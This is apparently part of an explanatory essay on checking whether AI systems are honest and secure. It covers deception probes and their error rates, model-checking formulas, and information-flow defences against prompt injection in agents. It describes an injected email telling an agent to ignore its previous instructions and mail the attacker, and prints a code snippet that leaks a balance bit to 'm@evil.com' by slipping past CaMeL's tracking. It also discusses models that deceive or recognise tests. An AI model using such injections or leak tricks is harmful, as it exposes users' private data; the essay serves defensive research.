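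| Detector | Lies caught | Lies missed | False alarms | Share of alarms that are lies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Deception probe, as first reported | 96 | 4 | 99 | 49% |
| The same probe, corrected | 73 | 27 | 99 | 42% |
| *AgentDecept* probe, 1% false alarms | 19 | 81 | 99 | 16% |
| *AgentDecept* probe, 2% false alarms | 57 | 43 | 198 | 22% |

The *AgentDecept* rows apply its rates to 10,000 records of an agent's work rather than to single statements. The probe with the AUROC of 0.979 misses 81 of the 100 lies at the stricter setting. Its AUROC can still be high because AUROC averages over all thresholds, most of which would allow far more false alarms.

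The false alarm rate could be higher in practice, because *AgentDecept* measured it on neutral material, and honest replies in tense situations may look more like lies. If only one statement in 1,000 were a lie, then in 10,000 statements the corrected deception probe would catch about 7 of the 10 lies and raise about 100 false alarms.

Whether this is good enough depends on the purpose. Cooney and colleagues distinguish two hopes for lie detectors. The weak hope is that they can help auditors alongside other tools. The strong hope is that they can support confident claims about what a model believes, for example that there is at least a 95% probability that it does not believe it has a certain goal. The corrected probe is useful for the weak hope, because a person would have to check only 172 flagged statements instead of 10,000 and would find 73 of the 100 lies. For that purpose, it wouldn't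 matter much if the probe detected misbehaviour in general rather than lying.

Supporters of reading activations mostly defend it as a research direction, not on the strength of current results. Anthropic argued early on that it may be very hard for a model to deceive without "thinking" about deception, which should leave traces in its activations. *The Promise of White-Box Tools for Detecting and Mitigating AI Deception* (2026), by researchers at FAR.AI, argues that methods limited to a model's outputs have structural weaknesses and that internal representations are more promising. Cooney and colleagues also favour more research on lie detection, but consider the strong hope far out of reach for current methods.

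### A probe inside a model checker

The honesty formula needs the strong hope, since it covers every statement in every run. Suppose an analyst gives the model checker a new basic fact, probe_φ, which is true at a point if the probe's score for φ is above the threshold there. The formula to check is then

```
AG ( says_i φ  ⇒  probe_φ )
```

A linear probe is just another weighted sum, so the analyst can treat it as an extra output of the network. If the network is as small as the ones researchers can already verify, a checker could in principle give an exact proof that, for every input in a given range, the network does not assert φ while the probe's score is too low.

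To conclude that the network is honest, the analyst needs a second premise:

```
AG ( probe_φ  ⇒  B_i φ )
```

Together, the two formulas imply that the network asserts φ only if it believes φ. But the checker can't prove the second formula, because the model contains no separate definition of B_i φ. Its only support is experiments like those above. The analyst could make it true by defining belief as the probe's output, but then the conclusion would again be only about the probe.

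Suppose the probe in fact detects obedience, and the network has instructions to say "heads" whatever the coin shows. Every time it says "heads" it is obeying, so the probe's score is high and the first formula is true in all runs. That includes the runs where the coin shows tails and the network would say so if asked neutrally. Checking more runs doesn't help, because the probe makes the same mistake in each.

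False alarms cause the opposite problem, since one exception is enough to make an AG formula false. Suppose the network is always honest, but the probe has a 1% chance of wrongly flagging each statement, independently of the others. The chance that 100 statements pass without a false alarm is 0.99^100, or about 37%. For 1,000 statements it is less than 1 in 20,000. After a false alarm, the checker would report a counterexample, and the analyst would need some other way to measure the network's beliefs to find out whether the flagged statement was a lie.

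## Which claims about AI systems can already be checked this way?

Showing that a model believes what it says requires measuring its beliefs. It is easier to show that the model could not have known something, because that depends only on what information reached it.

### From the same inputs to ignorance

Suppose Alice tosses her coin and puts the cup over it after a company has finished training a language model. Someone then asks the model which side is up. The argument below shows from the definition of K, not from an experiment, that the model doesn't know.

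1. Take a run r in which the coin is heads, and a run r′ in which it is tails but everything that reached the model is the same, including the training data and the prompt.
2. Training and answering also use random numbers. If these are independent of how the coin landed, then whatever numbers came up in r could equally have come up with tails, so let r′ have the same ones.
3. The model's weights and activations are the result of a calculation on these inputs and random numbers. The calculation is the same in both runs, so its results are too.
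4. The model therefore has the same local state in r and r′, whichever of its internal numbers the analyst counts as part of that state.
5. "The coin is heads" is true in r and false in r′. So the model does not know in r that the coin is heads, and it does not know in r′ that the coin is tails.

Balliu and colleagues reason in the same way about someone who watches a program's output. Here the model is the observer.

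Three earlier difficulties disappear. The choice of readout doesn't matter, because every readout gives the same value for identical activations. The assumption of logical omniscience does no harm, because even a perfect reasoner with these inputs would not know the fact. One alternative run is enough, without a list of every possible run, because adding more runs cannot turn ignorance of a plain fact into knowledge.

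The first step is the difficult one, because the inputs may not be the same even if nobody told the model the answer. If Alice asks the question only when the coin is heads, the question reveals the answer and r′ is not a possible run. If a hospital removes a patient's name from a record but leaves her postcode and date of birth, a model that reads the record may still be able to identify her. The timing of a request can also carry information. The argument doesn't apply to most general knowledge, because if the facts were different, the training data would be too.

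The argument can't show what the model believes, either. The model might be convinced in both runs that the coin landed heads. The argument shows only that this conviction doesn't depend on how the coin landed.

### Keeping an attacker's text away from decisions

A *language-model agent* is a language model that can call tools, such as programs that read email, run code or transfer money. Ordinary software passes text to the model, carries out its tool calls and returns the results. People wrote this software's rules and variables explicitly, unlike the model's weights, so an analyst can prove facts about what reaches the model and what the model's output can affect.

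The main reason to do this so far has been *prompt injection*, in which an attacker hides instructions in text that the agent reads. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One email contains instructions for the agent to ignore its previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to the attacker. Filters may detect such an email, but they aren't guaranteed to.

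Information-flow control instead labels data according to where they came from. *SPA* (2026) distinguishes *confidentiality* labels, which record how sensitive the data are, from *integrity* labels, which record how far to trust them. Both can support ignorance claims. Confidentiality means that outsiders don't learn the secret. Integrity holds in its strictest form if the part of the system that chooses actions doesn't know what the untrusted text says, because then its choices can't depend on that text.

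CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, divides the work between two models. Based on the description in *CaMeLoT* (2026), it would handle the email request roughly like this:

1. A privileged model, which sees the user's request but none of the emails, writes a short program: find the emails about the project, get a summary, send it to the manager.
2. An interpreter runs the program. It passes the emails to a quarantined model, which writes the summary but can't call any tools.
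3. The interpreter stores the summary with tags that record where it came from and who may read it.
4. Before sending the summary, the interpreter checks the tags against a policy.

The privileged model has no access to the contents of the emails, so it writes the same program whatever the attacker put in them. The attacker can still spoil the summary but can't add a step to the program. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends this separation to groups of agents, where an injected instruction may arrive in a message from another agent.

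The drawback is that some tasks require the planner to know what the data contain. Costa and colleagues call a task *data independent* if a single sequence of tool calls and a single final response would be right whatever the data contain. "Do the tasks due today in my to-do app" is not data independent, because the right tool calls depend on what's on the list. Their system, FIDES, therefore lets some information through. A quarantined model can read the hidden data and return an answer in a fixed format, such as yes or no. An attacker may be able to change that answer but can't use it to pass on an instruction.

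Most of the tests use AgentDojo, a benchmark that measures whether agents can finish their tasks despite injected text meant to divert them. The table's CaMeL results come from *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) and *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) by Garby, Gordon and Sands, who also built the agent in the third row. The last row is from *APPA* (2026).

| System | Successful attacks | Effect on ordinary tasks |
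|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | almost none | on banking tasks, turning on the policy checks halves its usefulness |
| FIDES | none, with suitable policies | 6.3% less useful than a basic agent with the checks off; with them on, it completes 8% more tasks using GPT-4o and 16% more using o1 |
| LLMbda agent | 2 in 1,296 attacked runs, on banking tasks | about as useful as CaMeL without its checks |
| APPA | none in 1,320 runs, on other benchmarks | 64.2–91% usefulness |

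Simpler systems treat everything an agent produces after reading untrusted data as untrusted. This is a common reason an agent becomes less useful, since it soon can't do anything important. APPA offers the agent a permitted way to continue instead of aborting the task.

The policies matter as much as the labels. Costa and colleagues found that without policy checks, practical attacks still worked on every system they tested, including FIDES. *SPA* points out that when people write a separate policy for each tool, the guarantee depends on every policy being correct and complete.

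Labels are also hard to track through the model itself. A model mixes everything in its context, so a cautious system has to assume that each answer depends on all of it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests that a faithful account of the model's internal mechanism might show which inputs an answer depends on, but this would again require examining the inside of the network.

### A leak that no single run reveals

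Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's tracking of secrets has gaps. Suppose an injected instruction tries to find out whether a customer's balance is above some threshold. CaMeL blocks a program that checks the balance and then sends an email if it is high. But the program can take a detour, using a trick that Fenton described decades ago:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:   tmp  = False
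if tmp:                   rich = False
if rich:                  send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret if the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. There are two cases:

| Balance | tmp | rich | Does the attacker get an email? |
|---|---|---|---|
| above the threshold | False, marked secret | True, not marked | yes |
| not above it | True, not marked | False, not marked | no |

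When the balance is high, the program skips the line that would change rich, so CaMeL never marks that variable as secret. The value of rich reveals the secret, but CaMeL treats it as public and lets the email through. A monitor that follows only the lines that a run executes can't detect this leak, because the attacker learns from the skipped line. Detecting it requires comparing the run where the balance is high with one where it is low.

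The other gap is outside the interpreter, in the ordinary Python code that tries again when a policy blocks the program. Nothing tracks what an attacker can learn from whether the policy blocked it. One attempt reveals at most one bit, but an attacker who can keep triggering attempts can extract a whole secret.

LLMbda is a small programming language for agents that closes such gaps by labelling every value. Garby and colleagues proved that it satisfies a version of noninterference, the requirement that secrets have no effect on what an observer sees. Lean, a proof-checking program, checked the proof, which covers every program in the language, including those a model writes while the agent is running. The proof does not rule out that an observer could learn something about a secret from whether a program finishes.

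The theorem treats the language model as a black box that draws each response from a probability distribution depending only on the conversation so far, so it holds for any model. This is a much more general form of the argument from inputs.

Programs in LLMbda can also isolate conversations. An agent can copy its conversation, let the model read an untrusted email in the copy, extract a date and then discard the copy. The model's later responses can't depend on the email unless the program passes the date on, and the date is still labeled "untrusted". To treat the date as trusted, a programmer has to write an explicit instruction, which a reviewer can find.

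None of these guarantees makes the model competent or honest. As Costa and colleagues note, a model can misunderstand a user even when all the data are trustworthy.

### Proving that an agent could not have known

The argument from inputs applies to one part of honesty, because a record of an agent's inputs can prove that the agent had no way of knowing something it asserted.

Suppose a coding agent changes a program and sends it to a separate server, which runs the tests. The connection breaks before any result comes back. The agent then tells the user, "All tests passed." Two runs are possible:

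| Run | What happens on the server | What reaches the agent | What the agent says |
|---|---|---|---|
| r1 | all tests pass | "connection lost" | "All tests passed" |
| r2 | the server runs out of memory and a test fails | "connection lost" | "All tests passed" |

Let passed mean that all the tests on the server passed, and let received_i mean that agent i has received information about the result. The honesty formula for this statement is

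```
AG ( says_i passed  ⇒  K_i passed )
```

By the argument from inputs, an agent that has received no such information doesn't know the result:

```
AG ( ¬received_i  ⇒  ¬K_i passed )
```

If both formulas are true, so is

```
AG ( says_i passed  ⇒  received_i )
```

The agent in the example breaks this last rule. The second formula is true, so the honesty formula must be false. Checking this doesn't require knowing what happened on the server. The agent has overclaimed even in r1, where its statement happens to be true.

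The last rule doesn't depend on what anyone knows and concerns one run at a time, so an ordinary program can enforce it. If the agent has to report test results in a separate field, the surrounding software could reject "passed" there unless the value came from the test server. CaMeL's tags already record where values came from.

This proof works only if the record includes everything from which the agent could have learned the result, such as notes from an earlier session or a message from another agent, and the result depends on something the agent didn't receive. If the agent has read the program and all the tests, then whether the program *would* pass them on a perfect computer may be a mathematical consequence of what it has read, and by logical omniscience the agent then counts as knowing the answer. The example avoids this problem because the claim is about what happened on a particular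 server, which might have run out of memory.

An agent can overclaim without lying. It may have mistaken an old result for a new one and believed what it said, in which case it satisfies the version of the honesty formula that uses B. The record is also less informative when a result did arrive. If the server reported three failures and the agent says that all tests passed, the record proves that the statement is false, but not that the agent noticed the failures.

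### Does the model know it is being tested?

"The model does not know that it is being tested" is also an ignorance claim, ¬K_i test. Evaluators want it to be true because a model that recognises a test might behave well only during tests. They could guarantee it by using only inputs that the model would be equally likely to receive in ordinary use. Its internal state and behaviour would then have the same probability distributions in both settings, whatever it suspected.

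But an invented scenario may have no exact counterpart in ordinary use, and then the argument from inputs doesn't apply. A model that suspects it is being tested doesn't know that it is, but the suspicion can still change its behaviour unless it is just as suspicious of real users. Developers can also monitor a model in ordinary use, but *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026), from the UK's AI Security Institute, reports that several of the properties that make monitoring possible are weakening.

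### Proof has become cheaper

Proofs about the software around a model used to take too much work for most projects. Verifying seL4, the core of an operating system, took about 20 person-years. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes how Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries, in a project with the company Theorem.

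*Pre-QED* (Lim, Tu and colleagues, 2026) describes how the project worked. The libraries already had *fuzz harnesses*, small test programs that feed a library random data to see whether it crashes. The project's software turned each harness into a mathematical statement that the compiled program does not crash on any input smaller than 64 MB. Claude then wrote a proof, typically about 600,000 lines long, and the proof checker Rocq verified it. If Claude found a bug, it repaired the library first. Because Claude could have cheated by rewriting a program to do almost nothing and therefore never crash, the project penalised and recorded changes to the code. The project covered 239 harnesses and uncovered hundreds of bugs.

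*Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (2026) reports a similar effort on a whole operating system kernel, xv6. The proof, produced with AI agents, took 102 days from the first idea and is about 1.6 million lines long, for a kernel of 6,657 lines.

The checker verifies these proofs, so nobody has to read them. People still have to trust the checker, the mathematical model of the computer, and the statement that the proof establishes. The model can be wrong. For example, the xv6 project found a bug in an established model of the RISC-V processor, as well as 11 bugs in xv6 itself.

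### Someone still has to choose what to prove

Lim and colleagues show how a correct proof can miss a bug. In their example, a library lets a program read a data stream in pieces. The library is supposed to stop at the end of the stream, but it compares the size of each request with the length of the whole stream instead of the part that remains. If a program asks for 40 bytes twice from a 64-byte stream, the second request starts at byte 40 and runs 16 bytes past the end.

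The fuzz harness opens the stream, reads once and closes it. One can prove that the harness never crashes, but any program that reads twice can trigger the bug. The proof doesn't cover those runs, just as a proof about a protocol model doesn't cover an attack that the model omits.

Lim and colleagues therefore built harnesses for 29 libraries that are meant to allow every legal sequence of calls, which they describe partly in temporal logic. Proving properties of such harnesses is harder because a sequence can be any length. They think the bottleneck has moved from working out how to prove properties to deciding which ones to prove.

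This is more urgent now that so many new proofs are appearing. In *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (2026), Keles argues that people should stop calling software "formally verified" and instead name its verified properties. He is optimistic about the technology but points out that a mistaken definition can undermine a proof even when the checker accepts it.

The choice of property also limits which tools one can use. TLA+, a popular language for specifying software, checks properties of individual runs. Wayne (2026), in *What TLA+ can and can't check*, explains that TLA+ can't directly express properties that involve several runs, such as noninterference. Users can sometimes get around this by putting two copies of a system into one model and comparing them.

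Wayne also points out that nobody can prove an app recognises birds if nobody can define a bird formally, and no tool can remove that limit. "The test result never reached the model" is a statement about software, and an AI system could now write much of the proof. But nobody has yet expressed "the model believes that the tests passed" as a statement about weights and activations that an AI system could try to prove.
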